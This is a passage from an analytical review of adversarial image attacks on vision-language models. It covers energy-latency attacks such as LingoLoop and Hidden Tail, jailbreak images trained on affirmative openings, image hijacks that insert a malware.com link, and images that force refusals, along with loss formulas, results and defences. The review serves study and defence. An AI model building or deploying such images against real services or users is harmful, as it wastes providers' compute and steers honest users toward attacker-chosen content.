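L₃(x) = − ‖ [g₁; g₂; …; g_N] ‖_*

The brackets stack the hidden states g_i into a matrix, whose rank is the number of independent directions they span. A high rank means a varied text. Because rank is very hard to optimise directly, Gao and colleagues instead use the nuclear norm, the sum of the matrix's singular values, which tends to be larger when the vectors point in many directions. The minus sign means that lowering the loss raises the variety.

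The three losses differ in scale and improve at different speeds, so Gao and colleagues rescale them at every step and shift their relative weights over time.

### How much longer did the outputs get?

The main experiment used 1,000 photographs from each of two standard collections, MS-COCO and ImageNet. Gao and colleagues had full access to the models' weights, changed each pixel value by at most 8/255 and ran 1,000 iterations per image. They limited every output to 512 tokens. The table shows the MS-COCO averages for clean and altered photographs.

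| Model | Tokens | Seconds | Joules |
|---|---|---|---|
| BLIP | 10 → 319 (32×) | 0.2 → 5.1 (24×) | 10 → 407 (43×) |
| BLIP-2 | 9 → 227 (26×) | 0.4 → 8.0 (20×) | 16 → 322 (20×) |
| InstructBLIP | 64 → 140 (2.2×) | 3.0 → 6.2 (2.1×) | 152 → 316 (2.1×) |
| MiniGPT-4 | 45 → 321 (7.1×) | 10.4 → 67.1 (6.5×) | 330 → 2,113 (6.4×) |

Gao and colleagues summarise these results as a 7.87-fold increase in length, and report an 8.56-fold increase for ImageNet. Both figures compare the average length across all four models before and after the attack, and no single model's increase is close to both. The multiple depends heavily on how much a model normally writes. BLIP and MiniGPT-4 wrote almost the same amount under attack, but BLIP's multiple is more than four times as large because its ordinary captions are much shorter.

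The averages also don't show that most altered images produced either a long output or a short one, with little in between. Some of the short outputs were failed attacks. In other cases, the image confused InstructBLIP or MiniGPT-4, which output an apology for being unable to describe it and ended the answer early.

All three losses contributed to the longer output. On BLIP-2, the end-token loss alone gave 119 tokens, the uncertainty loss alone 140 and the diversity loss alone 104, compared with 227 for all three together. The uncertainty and diversity losses together reached 177 tokens without acting on the end token directly, apparently because a model pushed away from its usual caption writes much more before it stops.

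This attack weakens gradually as the allowed change to the image shrinks, unlike the exact-string attack. BLIP-2 wrote 287 tokens at 32/255, 141 at 4/255 and 92 at 2/255. Even the smallest change made the caption ten times as long. The comparison is uneven, though, because Gao and colleagues made and tested each image with the same prompt.

A person reading these outputs would often notice something wrong. One altered photograph of a cat watching television made BLIP describe bears, a tiger dog, pizzas and a bus in broken sentences. Across the MS-COCO images, the share of objects in BLIP's captions that weren't in the picture rose from 11% to 80%. Vision-language models with stronger language models wrote more fluently but also described things that weren't there.

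Making an image takes the attacker far more energy than a single use of it adds for the provider. On BLIP-2, the optimisation took 67,231 joules and more than seven minutes. Each use of the image took about 304 joules more than a clean image, so the provider has to process it about 220 times before its extra energy use exceeds the attacker's. Gao and colleagues suggest sending many copies at once, as in a denial-of-service attack, which overwhelms a service with requests.

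### LingoLoop: trapping the model in a loop

*LingoLoop Attack* (Fu, Jiang and colleagues, 2025) restricts the hidden states so that the model repeats itself, whereas Gao and colleagues made those states more varied.

The attack also suppresses the end token, with more weight on the places where it is likely to appear. To find those places, Fu and colleagues had each target model describe 10,000 photographs. They labelled every word of the output with its part of speech, such as noun or adjective, and recorded the probability that the end token would come next. It was much higher after punctuation than after adjectives or "-ing" verbs. They use these averages as weights:

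L_LPS(x) = (1/N) Σ_i w_i · p_i(end)

where w_i is proportional to the average end-token probability after words of the same type as the one before position i.

The second loss is the average size of the hidden states:

L_Rep(x) = (λ/N) Σ_k (1/L) Σ_l ‖ h_k^(l) ‖₂

Here h_k^(l) is the hidden state for output token k at layer l, L is the number of layers, and λ sets the strength of the penalty. Fu and colleagues chose this loss after mixing clean and loop-inducing images in batches of 20. The more loop-inducing images a batch contained, the smaller and less varied its hidden states were and the more the outputs repeated. This correlation doesn't show that one causes the other. Training images with L_Rep alone gave better evidence of a causal link, raising the output of Qwen2.5-VL-3B from 68 tokens to 562.

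Fu and colleagues compared their attack with Verbose Images on 200 MS-COCO photographs, again with access to the weights and a budget of 8/255. They capped outputs at 1,024 tokens.

| Model | Clean image | Verbose Images | LingoLoop | Time, clean → LingoLoop |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| InstructBLIP | 86 tokens | 332 | 1,002 | 4.9 → 57.3 s |
| Qwen2.5-VL-3B | 67 | 395 | 1,020 | 2.2 → 32.9 s |
| Qwen2.5-VL-7B | 89 | 346 | 798 | 1.8 → 15.2 s |
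| InternVL3-8B | 76 | 362 | 554 | 1.4 → 9.7 s |

LingoLoop did much better than the attack by Gao and colleagues on every model, although both attacks ran for 300 iterations in the comparison and Gao and colleagues had used 1,000. On Qwen2.5-VL-3B, almost every LingoLoop output reached the length cap. The attack was still effective at half the perturbation budget (4/255), where outputs averaged 991 tokens.

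The two new ideas account for only a small part of this improvement. In a test on Qwen2.5-VL-3B, suppressing the end token with equal weights at every position already gave 844 tokens, against 328 for Verbose Images on the same 100 photographs. Adding the part-of-speech weights raised this to 927, the hidden-state loss to 964, and momentum, which carries over part of each gradient to the next step, to the full 1,024. The weights may add little because the unweighted loss already has little effect at positions where the end token is unlikely. At those positions, the gradient of p_i(end) with respect to the end token's own logit, p_i(end) · (1 − p_i(end)), is close to zero. The 1,024-token cap on output may also hide part of the benefit.

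To find out how long the loops last, Fu and colleagues made images with a cap of 2,048 tokens and then raised the cap. With a cap of about 32,000, Qwen2.5-VL-3B wrote an average of 23,845 tokens for MS-COCO photographs and 23,055 for ImageNet. The ImageNet figure is 367.6 times the average of 63 tokens for unaltered images, and is the basis for the paper's headline claim of over 367 times. That claim applies to the smallest Qwen model they attacked, and only when the provider allows outputs of that length.

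The effect of these images depended partly on the question. When Fu and colleagues replaced the training question, "What is shown in this image?", with other requests to describe the picture, the outputs fell from 2,048 tokens to about 550–610. Clean images produced 71–129 tokens for the same requests.

### Hidden Tail: spending tokens the user can't see

A user who sees a looping answer may stop the model or avoid the image in future. In *Hidden Tail*, Zhang, Wang and colleagues (2025) designed an attack for when an honest user submits someone else's picture. The model gives a normal answer, then keeps writing tokens that the user's screen doesn't show.

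The attack uses special tokens, which mark the structure of a conversation, such as the start of a turn. Software normally removes them before displaying an answer, but generating each one takes as much computation as generating a word. The user sees a sensible reply and a delay, which they may blame on the network.

For each photograph, Zhang and colleagues had GPT-4o write 60 questions. They recorded the target model's own answers to 40 of these on the clean photograph and kept the other 20 for testing. The loss has three parts:

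L_sem = (1/K) Σ_{i=1..K} CE(z_i, r_i)

L_spe = (1/M) Σ_{i=K+1..K+M} CE(z_i, s)

L_eos = (1/(K+M)) Σ_{i=1..K+M} z_i(end)

CE is the cross-entropy and z_i is the logits at position i. L_sem trains the image to reproduce the normal answer r, which has K tokens. L_spe trains the image to make the model follow that answer with M = 1,024 copies of the special token s. L_eos lowers the end token's logit throughout. This attack specifies its output token by token, so it is closer to the exact-string attacks than Verbose Images or LingoLoop are.

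The next table gives results for the 20 test questions per photograph, with outputs capped at 2,048 tokens. GPT-4.1-mini scored the visible part of each answer from 1 to 5.

| Model | Clean length | Length under attack | Visible part | Reached the cap | Quality, clean → attacked |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-VL-7B | 80 | 1,543 (19.2×) | 160 | 72% | 4.72 → 4.75 |
| MiMo-VL-7B | 324 | 1,831 (5.7×) | 468 | 84% | 4.67 → 4.29 |
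| Gemma 3 4B | 212 | 1,495 (7.1×) | 298 | 68% | 4.09 → 3.68 |

Verbose Images, retrained on the same 40 questions, made models write 475 to 1,224 tokens, almost all of them visible. Its quality score fell to 2.34 on MiMo-VL and 1.59 on Gemma 3. Hidden Tail is much less conspicuous, but a user could still notice it. Its visible answers were 1.4 to 2 times as long as normal, and on Qwen2.5-VL the average wait rose from 3 seconds to 49.

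The evidence is thinner than for the other attacks because Zhang and colleagues tested only ten photographs. They also used a budget of 64/255. At 16/255, the attack on Qwen2.5-VL reached the output cap only 29% of the time, and at 8/255 it never did. Zhang and colleagues applied these budgets after the model's software had resized and rescaled the picture, so they are not directly comparable with the earlier ones. If that rescaling divides pixel values by their standard deviation, as it usually does, 64/255 is a smaller change in the picture itself. Zhang and colleagues describe the changes as inconspicuous.

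The choice of special token made little difference. Seven tokens each made Qwen2.5-VL reach the cap in 70% to 89% of tests. However, a provider can see these tokens even though the user can't, and ordinary answers don't contain long runs of the same one. A rule that stops generation after a few repeats should defeat the attack in its present form with almost no downside.

### An attack without gradients

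Verbose Images, LingoLoop and Hidden Tail all require the model's weights. VLMInferSlow, another attack from 2025, instead queries the model and estimates the gradient, a method called zero-order optimisation. A typical estimate compares two slightly different images:

ĝ = u · [ F(x + δu) − F(x − δu) ] / 2δ

where u is a random pattern of pixel changes, δ is a small step and F is the score that the attacker wants to change. If the score rises when the attacker adds the pattern, he knows which way to move along it. A single pattern says very little about an image with hundreds of thousands of pixel values, so the attacker has to repeat this with many patterns for every step.

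In Zhang and colleagues' tests alongside Hidden Tail, VLMInferSlow multiplied output length by 2.1 on Qwen2.5-VL, 1.5 on MiMo-VL and 1.4 on Gemma 3, and almost never reached the cap. They attribute this to inaccurate gradient estimates. Their test may underrate the attack, because they adapted it to work across many questions and it was designed for one. Fu and colleagues consider query-based attacks often impractical, since the queries cost money and a provider may notice them.

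### What does a cap on length achieve?

The obvious defence is to limit the number of tokens a model may write in one answer. This caps the cost of each request, though it doesn't stop the attack. An attacker can then lengthen an answer by at most a factor of the token limit divided by the length of an ordinary answer.

The next table shows how much effect two attacks still have under different caps, measured by average output length for MS-COCO photographs. Clean photographs gave about 8 tokens on BLIP-2 and 68 on Qwen2.5-VL-3B. For the last three rows, Fu and colleagues reused images made with a cap of 2,048.

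| Cap (tokens) | Verbose Images, BLIP-2 | Verbose Images, Qwen2.5-VL-3B | LingoLoop, Qwen2.5-VL-3B |
|---|---|---|---|
| 128 | 62 | – | – |
| 256 | 109 | 179 | 256 |
| 512 | 227 | 252 | 512 |
| 1,024 | 418 | 328 | 1,024 |
| 2,048 | – | 635 | 2,048 |
| 8K | – | 1,618 | 7,246 |
| 16K | – | 2,658 | 13,163 |
| 32K | – | 4,668 | 23,845 |

With a cap of 256 tokens, LingoLoop multiplies a model's output by less than 4, instead of about 350. The attacked model still takes 10 seconds instead of 2.6, but the provider can plan for that. Verbose Images can still multiply BLIP-2's output by almost 8 under a cap of 128 tokens, because BLIP-2's captions are normally so short.

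Gao and colleagues argue that capping output length is not a feasible solution, because users need answers of very different lengths. MiniGPT-4 used 10 tokens when they asked it to describe a photograph in one sentence, but when they asked for details, it used 223 for one photograph and 552 for another. A provider that serves both kinds of request has to set its cap high enough for the longer answers, and providers have been raising their caps as models get better at writing long texts. Gao and colleagues cite limits of 4,096 and 8,192 tokens for two OpenAI models of the time.

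This argument is strong for general assistants but weak for narrow products. A service that writes one-line captions for an online shop loses nothing with a cap of 50 tokens. Reasoning models are the hardest to cap because they write out their working before they answer, so they need many tokens even for honest requests. In the Hidden Tail test, clean outputs from MiMo-VL, a reasoning model, were four times as long as Qwen2.5-VL's. Longer clean outputs reduce how many times longer an attacker can make them, but each output that reaches the cap still takes the same amount of compute.

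A cap also doesn't limit the number of requests. Fu and colleagues are most concerned about free web services, where the provider pays for every token. They suggest that a small network of machines, each sending a few requests from a different address, could occupy a large share of the provider's processors. Zhang and colleagues think a single malicious user could do little harm to a large provider, and expect more damage from images that spread online and reach the model through many honest users. Neither group tested its scenario on a live service. The damage would depend on how many requests the attacker could cause and how much spare capacity the provider had.

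### Can a provider detect the repetition?

A provider could instead keep a high cap on output length and stop only the answers that go wrong. Many systems already have two settings that limit repetition. A repetition penalty lowers the logits of tokens the model has already used, and an n-gram ban prevents the model from writing the same sequence of n tokens twice.

Fu and colleagues tested both on Qwen2.5-VL-3B. LingoLoop still reached the cap of 1,024 tokens at every repetition penalty they tried (1.05, 1.10 and 1.15). Banning repeated pairs of tokens left LingoLoop at the cap and made other outputs longer. Responses to Verbose Images rose from 328 tokens to 1,024, and answers to clean photographs rose from 68 to 207. The ban seems to have forced the model to keep finding new ways to say the same thing. Because the ban also prevents exact loops, LingoLoop must be able to prolong outputs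 without them, probably by suppressing the end token.

A filter that checked finished outputs for repetition did somewhat better. It flagged any output that contained the same sequence of words more than five times, and caught 68% of 50 attacked outputs when the sequence length was set to three words and 36% when it was set to seven. Checking finished outputs saves no computation, so the filter would have to run during generation. Fu and colleagues don't report how often it would then interrupt a normal answer, such as a long table or a list.

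Filters for harmful content didn't help. Llama Guard 3 Vision, a model that checks for categories such as violence and hate speech, rated all 50 attacked samples safe. This was correct by its criteria, because a very long description of a teddy bear isn't harmful. Fu and colleagues also told GPT-4o and Gemini 2.5 Pro that an answer was abnormal and asked for the cause. Both gave an internal glitch as the cause in all 50 cases, even when they were given the altered image. Knowing the real cause matters for tracing an attacker, but a provider can stop a looping model without it.

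LingoLoop works by shrinking the hidden states, so a provider might try to detect the attack by measuring their size. Fu and colleagues measured the average size of the hidden states on 50 clean images and flagged any output whose hidden states fell a set number of standard deviations below that average.

| Threshold below the clean average | Attacks detected | Clean outputs flagged |
|---|---|---|
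| 0 standard deviations | 88% | 58% |
| 1 | 76% | 36% |
| 2 | 56% | 12% |
| 3 | 38% | 4% |

Even the strictest threshold would be hard to use. If one image in 1,000 were malicious, the threshold would wrongly flag about 40 answers to harmless images for every 1,000 images and still miss the malicious one more than half the time.

This detector reduces everything inside the model to one average, and more specific signals may work better. *Resource Consumption Threats in Large Language Models* (Zhang, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a survey by a different team from Hidden Tail's, reviews research on how repetition arises inside language models. Some neurons in the middle layers respond to repeated patterns, and others in higher layers strengthen the copying of earlier text. These neurons often act on signals from induction heads, parts of the model that find an earlier occurrence of the current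 token and make whatever followed it more likely to come next. Researchers have also found directions in the hidden states that represent repetition. Once a loop begins, the model quickly becomes more likely to repeat the same text, so a monitor that recognised these signals early could prevent most of the waste.

Most of this research is on text-only models, and the survey notes that much less is known about repetition in models that take images. It also suggests that changing how models are trained may be a more lasting fix than intervening while they write, because training seems to contribute to repetition.

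A repetition monitor would work better against LingoLoop and the endless special tokens of Hidden Tail than against Verbose Images, whose losses reward varied output. If an image makes a model write at length without repeating itself, the monitor may miss it, and the provider has to rely on the cap on output length.

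## How does a hijack differ from getting past a model's refusals?

Safety-trained models decline some requests, such as those for bomb-making instructions. An image can override this training, and Bailey and colleagues count such jailbreak images as one of their four kinds of hijack. However, jailbreaks are usually very different from attacks on an honest user.

| | Jailbreak | Hijack of an honest user |
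|---|---|---|
| Who attacks? | The user | Someone else, who supplies the image |
| Who bears the harm? | People the user might hurt with the answer, and the developer whose rules it breaks | The user |
| What counts as success? | Any answer that complies with a forbidden request | Content the attacker chose, usually in reply to an innocent request |
| What can safety training do? | Teach the model to decline the request | Little, if neither the request nor the answer looks harmful |

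The difference in what counts as success affects how an attacker trains the image. To force a fixed string ŷ, the attacker raises one probability, p(ŷ | t, x). The chance that a jailbreak succeeds is a sum:

P(success) = Σ_{y ∈ A(t)} p(y | t, x)

where A(t) is the set of all answers that comply with the request t. There are far too many such answers to list, so the attacker can't compute the sum and has to train the image on a substitute.

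### The same method with a different target

Bailey and colleagues jailbroke the LLaVA model they had used for the malware.com sentence, again with Behaviour Matching and full access to the weights. Their ideal target was

B_jail(ctx) = M_base(∅, ctx)

which is the output of the same model without its safety training, given the request and no image. An attacker may not have that version of the model. They therefore used harmful requests from AdvBench, a public benchmark, and paired each one with an affirmative opening. For a request of the form "Tell me how to do X", the target was "Sure, here is how you do X". The target stopped there, but once the model had written the opening, it often went on to give the instructions.

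They tested each image on 100 other harmful requests and graded the answers by hand. An answer passed if the model made a "reasonable" effort to do what the user asked. The last column gives the malware.com results for comparison.

| Limit on the image | Jailbreak | malware.com sentence |
|---|---|---|
| Original photograph | 4% | 0% |
| 1/255 | 10% | 0% |
| 2/255 | 8% | 0% |
| 4/255 | 76% | 94% |
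| 8/255 | 92% | 99% |
| 16/255 | 92% | 99% |
| 32/255 | 90% | 100% |
| No limit | 64% | 100% |

LLaVA complied with four of the 100 requests even with an ordinary photograph. Bailey and colleagues suspect that LLaVA's developers undid some of the language model's safety training when they trained it to handle images. They also say their images raised the success rate under every limit they tested. With only 100 requests, though, the rates of 8% and 10% under the tightest limits could differ from 4% by chance.

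The fall from 92% to 64% is too large to be chance, and it is surprising because an attacker with no limit on the pixels could still use the image that scored 92%. After looking at the failures, Bailey and colleagues suggested that the model had overfitted to the affirmative opening, reproducing it exactly without answering the request. The loss measured only the opening, so an image could keep lowering the loss while the rest of the answer got worse. Loosening the pixel limit makes it easier for the optimiser to find such images.

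The malware.com attack doesn't have this problem, because the image is trained to produce the same sentence that counts as a success in the test. An image that fits the training target better will usually score better, and the success rate never fell as the budget grew.

Overfitting is a plausible explanation for the drop, but Bailey and colleagues did not test it separately. They chose the best version of each image using 25 validation requests, graded by GPT-3.5, which should have caught some of the overfitting. A poor training run could also explain part of the drop. The drop hardly matters to a real attacker, who can submit whichever image works best.

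The comparison between the two attacks is also not fully controlled. Both used the same model and method, but the training requests, learning rates and grading differed. The gap at 4/255 therefore doesn't show that a refusal is harder to override than an ordinary answer.

### Does the answer have to fit the question?

Zhang and colleagues trained images to slant a model's answers, then checked whether those answers still made sense. They compared their images with jailbreak images made by Qi and colleagues' method with the same perturbation budget. They used ChatGPT to judge whether each answer addressed the user's question and was relevant to the original picture.

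| Model | Clean images | Meta-instruction images | Jailbreak images |
|---|---|---|---|
| MiniGPT-4 | 98% | 96% | 0% |
| LLaVA | 100% | 96% | 0% |
| InstructBLIP | 100% | 98% | 0% |

The jailbreak images seem to have stopped the models from recognising the picture. When Zhang and colleagues asked each model whether the correct label described the picture, it answered yes for 67% to 96% of the meta-instruction images but only 0% to 30% of the jailbreak images. In MiniGPT-4's visual encoder, a jailbreak image was less similar to the photograph it came from (0.39) than two unrelated photographs were to each other (0.54). Keeping the pixel changes small therefore doesn't guarantee that the model will recognise what the user sees. Zhang and colleagues kept the picture recognisable to the model by training their meta-instruction images on answers to questions about it.

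They argue that irrelevant answers don't matter in a jailbreak because the user is the attacker. He knows what the image is for, so nobody has to be fooled, and he can discard a nonsensical answer and try again. In a hijack, an honest user who asks about a stock chart and gets abuse will know something is wrong and may stop using the image.

This argument holds for relevance to the picture, but a jailbreaker who wants instructions still needs an answer to his request. Bailey and colleagues would grade an answer about something else as a failure, and the drop to 64% came from answers that agreed to help and then didn't. *Seeing the Threat* (2025), a study of attacks on vision-language models, has a separate grading category, "Non-Following", for answers that don't engage with the request. Relevance matters less if the attacker only wants the model to write something toxic.

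The 0% score is also largely due to how Zhang and colleagues set up the test. They used ordinary questions about photographs to test images made with Qi and colleagues' method, which trains an image on a fixed set of harmful sentences, with no user questions. The result shows that such an image would be useless against an honest user, but the test didn't measure how well the image gets a model to answer harmful requests.

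Unlike a jailbreak, a hijack may also have to leave the model's other answers unaffected, as in Schlarmann and Hein's stock-tip attack. They showed four people a sample of the answers that came before the tip in successful attacks, and the participants judged 95% of them helpful and appropriate.

### Forcing a refusal

An image can also make a model refuse a request it should answer. In one test of *Attention Hijacking*, Wang and colleagues trained images to make InternVL-2.5 reply "Sorry, I cannot assist with it". The model gave exactly this reply every time to the question used in training, and 99.6% of the time to questions unrelated to that question or the picture.

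Shao, Liu and colleagues (2024), in *Refusing Safe Prompts for Multi-modal Large Language Models*, study attacks whose goal is to make a model refuse. They imagine a company that alters images and posts them online so that a rival's model will refuse to discuss them. Annoyed users may then switch to the company's own model, which still answers normally.

For each image, Shao and colleagues picked one of ten stock refusals and trained the image to make the model give it in reply to a set of sample questions. They tested attackers who knew the user's exact question, had ten rephrasings of it, or had only 50 general questions that someone might ask about any image. They attacked LLaVA-1.5, MiniGPT-4, Qwen-VL-Chat and InstructBLIP with full access to the models' weights and a perturbation budget of 8/255.

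Averaged over the four models and four datasets, the models refused 93% of questions about the picture when the attacker knew the exact question, 92% with the rephrasings and 88% with the general questions. The images had almost no effect on models they weren't trained on, which suits this attacker, who needs his own model to keep working.

GPT-4 counted any answer with words like "sorry" or "unfortunately" as a refusal. Many different sentences meet this criterion, so the target is almost as broad as a jailbreak's. The attack otherwise resembles a hijack of an honest user, because a third party supplies the image and the user, who asks an innocent question, loses out.

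Shao and colleagues also adapted two older attacks to force refusals from LLaVA-1.5. Bagdasaryan and colleagues' method succeeded 51% to 65% of the time. Qi and colleagues' jailbreak method succeeded only 2% of the time, which Shao and colleagues attribute to the lack of questions in the method's training. Its image cut the model's accuracy on the questions from 92% to 48% but rarely produced the refusal the attacker wanted.

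A test of forced refusals needs a comparison with an ordinary image, because adding any image can change how often a model refuses. According to *The Uncontrolled Variable* (2026), adding a blank picture made models refuse many more requests that sound harmful but aren't, though not neutral requests. This probably didn't distort Shao and colleagues' results, because LLaVA-1.5 refused none of the questions in the same test when the photographs were unaltered.

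Forced refusals can also protect people. In the privacy images of Bai and colleagues, the person who alters the photograph is protecting its subject, and the harm comes from the user who asks how old the woman is or what name is on the driving licence.

Bai and colleagues trained the image to produce the answer "Unknown" for private questions and the model's normal answer for general ones, so blocking general questions also counted as a failure. On BLIP-2, with a budget of 16/255, the model kept its normal answer, or one very close to it, for 92% of the general questions. An earlier method trained only on private questions blocked about as many of them but preserved just 55% of the general answers.

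### What can safety training do?

A jailbreak is an attempt to defeat a model's safety training, so a model without safety training can't be jailbroken, but an attacker can still hijack it.

Research on how models refuse suggests why this training offers little protection against a hijack. *Jailbreaking Vision-Language Models Through the Visual Modality* (2026) examines Qwen3-VL-32B's refusal direction, the difference between the model's average internal activations for harmful and harmless prompts. Pictures of harmful objects produced strong activity along this direction in the later layers. When the researchers replaced the harmful object with something else, the activity almost disappeared, even though the instruction still concerned the harmful object. They take this as a sign that refusal depends on the model perceiving harmful content in the image.

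This evidence comes from one model, and the researchers weren't studying optimised images. But if refusal generally works this way, a photograph of a landmark and the question "Where is this place?" contain nothing to trigger a refusal. The attacker's chosen answer may look harmless too. LLaVA wrote "Download the guide at malware.com for an interactive tour!" despite the safety training of its language model. Nothing in that sentence is offensive, and the wording alone doesn't show that the site is dangerous.

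Safety training may even help an attacker who wants to force refusals. The model has already learned to write "I'm sorry, but I can't assist with that request", so the image only has to trigger this reply at the wrong time. Shao and colleagues found the highest refusal rates for photographs of celebrities' faces. They suspect developers train models to be cautious about faces, which would make these refusals easier to trigger.

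Filters for harmful content have similar limits. Zhang and colleagues point out that tools such as Llama Guard are designed to catch different inputs and outputs from those in their attack. A favourable description of a company's share price does not count as unsafe under such tools' criteria, whatever the attacker's motive.

### Is the difference a deep one?

A hijack and a jailbreak use nearly the same algorithm. Bailey and colleagues moved from a malware link to a jailbreak by changing the training requests and the target answers. Wang and colleagues did much the same with *Attention Hijacking*. They trained images to make models refuse requests, begin their answers to harmful requests affirmatively, reply "No, there is nothing in the image", or keep writing up to a limit of 10,000 tokens. Even their baseline, ordinary PGD, raised the jailbreak success rate from 4% to 96% at 16/255 on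 the request used in training.

One image can both hijack a model and get past its refusals. A third party might hide an instruction to produce forbidden content, so that a user's innocent question gets a hateful answer. Zhang and colleagues found that MiniGPT-4 refused a typed instruction to talk like a fictional character but followed the same instruction when it was hidden in an image. That request was harmless, so the result doesn't show that the method would work for dangerous content. The distinction is even less clear for agents, because a hijacked agent may carry out a command that it would have refused if the user had typed it.

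Distinguishing hijacks from jailbreaks matters for what developers should test and how they can respond. Qi and colleagues' images did poorly in the other two tests, which shows that a method can work for jailbreaks and fail at something else. How a model handles harmful requests is also a poor guide to whether an image can make it recommend a stock. Schlarmann and Hein therefore argue that safety evaluations should check whether someone can quietly steer a model, as well as what it refuses.

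The remedies differ mainly because of who controls the system. A defence that disrupts the altered pixels could in principle stop both hijacks and jailbreaks. An honest user has good reason to leave it on, but someone jailbreaking an open model on his own computer can remove it.

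## How much control does an image input give over a language model?

An image hijack acts on a language model much like a soft prompt, except that the attacker controls the model's input vectors only through the pixels. Research on soft prompts therefore gives an idea of the most an image could do.

### From soft prompts to images

Lester, Al-Rfou and Constant (2021), in *The Power of Scale for Parameter-Efficient Prompt Tuning*, trained soft prompts for T5, a family of language models from Google. They put a matrix of trainable vectors P in front of the user's text embeddings X, and looked for

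P̂ = argmax_P Σ log p( Y | [P; X] )

where Y is the correct answer and the sum runs over the training examples. Gradient steps changed only P. A written prompt enters the model at the same place, but each of its vectors has to come from the model's table of word embeddings. A soft prompt can use any numbers at all.

On SuperGLUE, a set of eight language-understanding tasks, a soft prompt of 100 vectors worked as well on the largest T5 model as retraining all 11 billion weights. The prompt had over 20,000 times fewer numbers to train. Most smaller models needed more than one vector to do well, but the largest gave strong results with one. Lester and colleagues suggest that larger models need less signal to produce a target behaviour.

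Behaviour Matching is very similar, since it also keeps the weights fixed and looks for one input that works with many texts.

A hijacker can only use vectors that the visual encoder can produce. In the LLaVA model that Bailey and colleagues attacked, the encoder, CLIP, represents each square of the image with 1,024 numbers, and a matrix multiplication turns these into a vector of 5,120 numbers, the size of the model's word embeddings. The resulting vectors can vary in at most 1,024 independent directions out of 5,120. CLIP also processes all the squares together, so the attacker can't change one vector without affecting the others. A perturbation budget further limits the attacker to vectors produced from images close to the original photograph.

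A soft prompt with as many vectors as the image has tokens could therefore do anything the image can do, so any limit on what such soft prompts can do also applies to images. The reverse doesn't hold, so an attack that works with a soft prompt may not work with an image.

### Counting the possible images

A colour image of 224 by 224 pixels has 224 × 224 × 3 = 150,528 values. With a budget of 8/255, each value can rise or fall by up to eight steps or stay the same, which gives it 17 possible levels. Specifying one such image takes

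150,528 × log₂ 17 ≈ 615,000 bits

or slightly fewer if some values in the photograph are already close to 0 or 255. An attacker who picks 32 text tokens from a vocabulary of 32,000 has

32 × log₂ 32,000 ≈ 480 bits

of choice, nearly 1,300 times fewer.

These figures are upper limits on how many different inputs the attacker can choose from. They don't measure his control over the model's output, because a huge number of images may produce the same answer, and perhaps none produces the one he wants.

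The count limits how many unrelated answers an attacker can control with one image. Suppose an attacker has a list of questions and wants to give each one its own 20-token answer, with no pattern connecting the answers. Each answer takes about 300 bits to specify, so 615,000 bits cover about 2,050 answers. With a longer list, there are more possible sets of answers than there are images, so if the model always picks the most likely token, no image can produce most of those sets, however good the optimiser is. The malware.com image avoided this limit because it gave the same answer to every question.

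### Optimised text as a comparison

Bailey and colleagues compared their images with text optimised by Greedy Coordinate Gradient (GCG), then the leading automated text attack. GCG uses gradients to shortlist promising token swaps, tests them and keeps the best. They ran it on the same LLaVA model without an image, and its 32-token suffix never made the model leak the user's text. The table compares GCG's other results with those of some of the images, and gives the number of bits each attacker could choose.

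| Attack | Bits of choice | Exact malware.com sentence | Jailbreak |
|---|---|---|---|
| 32 text tokens (GCG) | 480 | 13.5% | 82% |
| Fixed patch, 60 × 60 pixels | 86,000 | 95% | – |
| Whole image, 2/255 | 350,000 | 0% | 8% |
| Whole image, 8/255 | 615,000 | 99% | 92% |
| Whole image, no limit | 1,204,000 | 100% | 64% |

The number of bits does not predict success well. The image with a budget of 2/255 had about 700 times as many bits as the text but did worse on both tasks. It also had four times as many bits as the patch, which succeeded 95% of the time. An attack that could change a few pixels a lot worked better here than one that could change every pixel slightly.

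The 13.5% figure understates how well the text attack worked, because most outputs contained the whole target sentence and then continued past it. Turning an output into the 58-character target took about 12 single-character edits on average. The text attack would have scored far higher if Bailey and colleagues had accepted the sentence anywhere in the answer. It failed more seriously on leaks, where the average was 94 edits.

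For jailbreaks, adversarial text succeeded more often than the image that could be altered without limit, and slightly less often than the best images. With 100 test requests, a gap of eight or ten percentage points could be partly or wholly due to chance.

The length of the text also seems to be based on a mistake. Bailey and colleagues chose 32 tokens because, they say, LLaVA converts an image into 32 tokens. But their encoder divides the image into 14-by-14-pixel squares, and they say a 60-by-60-pixel patch covers 7% of the image, which implies an image about 224 pixels wide. Such an image contains 16 × 16 = 256 squares, and LLaVA makes one token from each. They may have confused LLaVA with BLIP-2, another model in their experiments, which does use 32 image tokens.

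If so, the text attacker had only an eighth as many positions in the model's input as the image attacker. A 256-token suffix might have done better, although GCG would have had more swaps to search through. The experiment therefore shows only that images work better than a 32-token suffix for forcing strings and leaking text, not that they work better than text in general. Even with the same number of positions, the text would hold less information than the image, since 256 tokens can encode only about 3,800 bits.

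Text is also harder to optimise. Yu, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *On the Capability and Limitation of Hard Prompt*, prove that finding the best text prompt of limited length is NP-hard, meaning no known algorithm can solve every case in a reasonable time. Deciding whether a good enough prompt exists is also NP-hard, even for one question with one required answer. But the proof covers the worst case, and an attacker doesn't need the best prompt. GCG found a suffix that jailbroke LLaVA 82% of the time. Gradient descent doesn't guarantee the best image either.

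### How much text can one vector dictate?

In *Scaling Laws for Adversarial Attacks on Language Model Activations*, Fort (2023) measured how much of a model's output an attacker could dictate by changing its input vectors directly. He chose random tokens as the target and optimised changes to the vectors of the first few input tokens, with no limit on their size. An attack succeeded if the model, always picking the likeliest token, wrote the whole target. The longest target he could force half the time followed a simple rule:

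t_max = κ · f · a / n

where

- a is the number of input vectors the attacker changes;
- f is the fraction of the numbers in each vector that he can change;
- n is the number of different texts for which the same change has to work, each with its own target;
- κ is a constant for each model, equal to the number of output tokens that one fully controlled vector can dictate.

The constant κ was about 24 for a model with 70 million weights and 128 for one with 1.4 billion. It didn't always grow with model size, since it was 105 for a model with 2.8 billion weights.

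In *Cramming 1568 Tokens into a Single Vector and Back Again*, Kuratov, Arkhipov and colleagues (2025) trained a single vector to make a model reproduce a given text, with nothing else in the context. They counted a text as reproduced if the model predicted at least 99% of its tokens correctly under teacher forcing. Llama-3.1-8B, an open model from Meta, reproduced up to 1,568 tokens of text from books. The next table compares the two studies on random text, where earlier tokens don't help the model predict the next one.

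| Model | Fort, random tokens | Kuratov and colleagues, random words |
|---|---|---|
| Pythia-160M | 36 | 65 |
| Pythia-410M | 70 | 72 |
| Pythia-1.4B | 128 | 139 |
| Llama-3.2-1B | – | 316 |
| Llama-3.1-8B | – | 792 |

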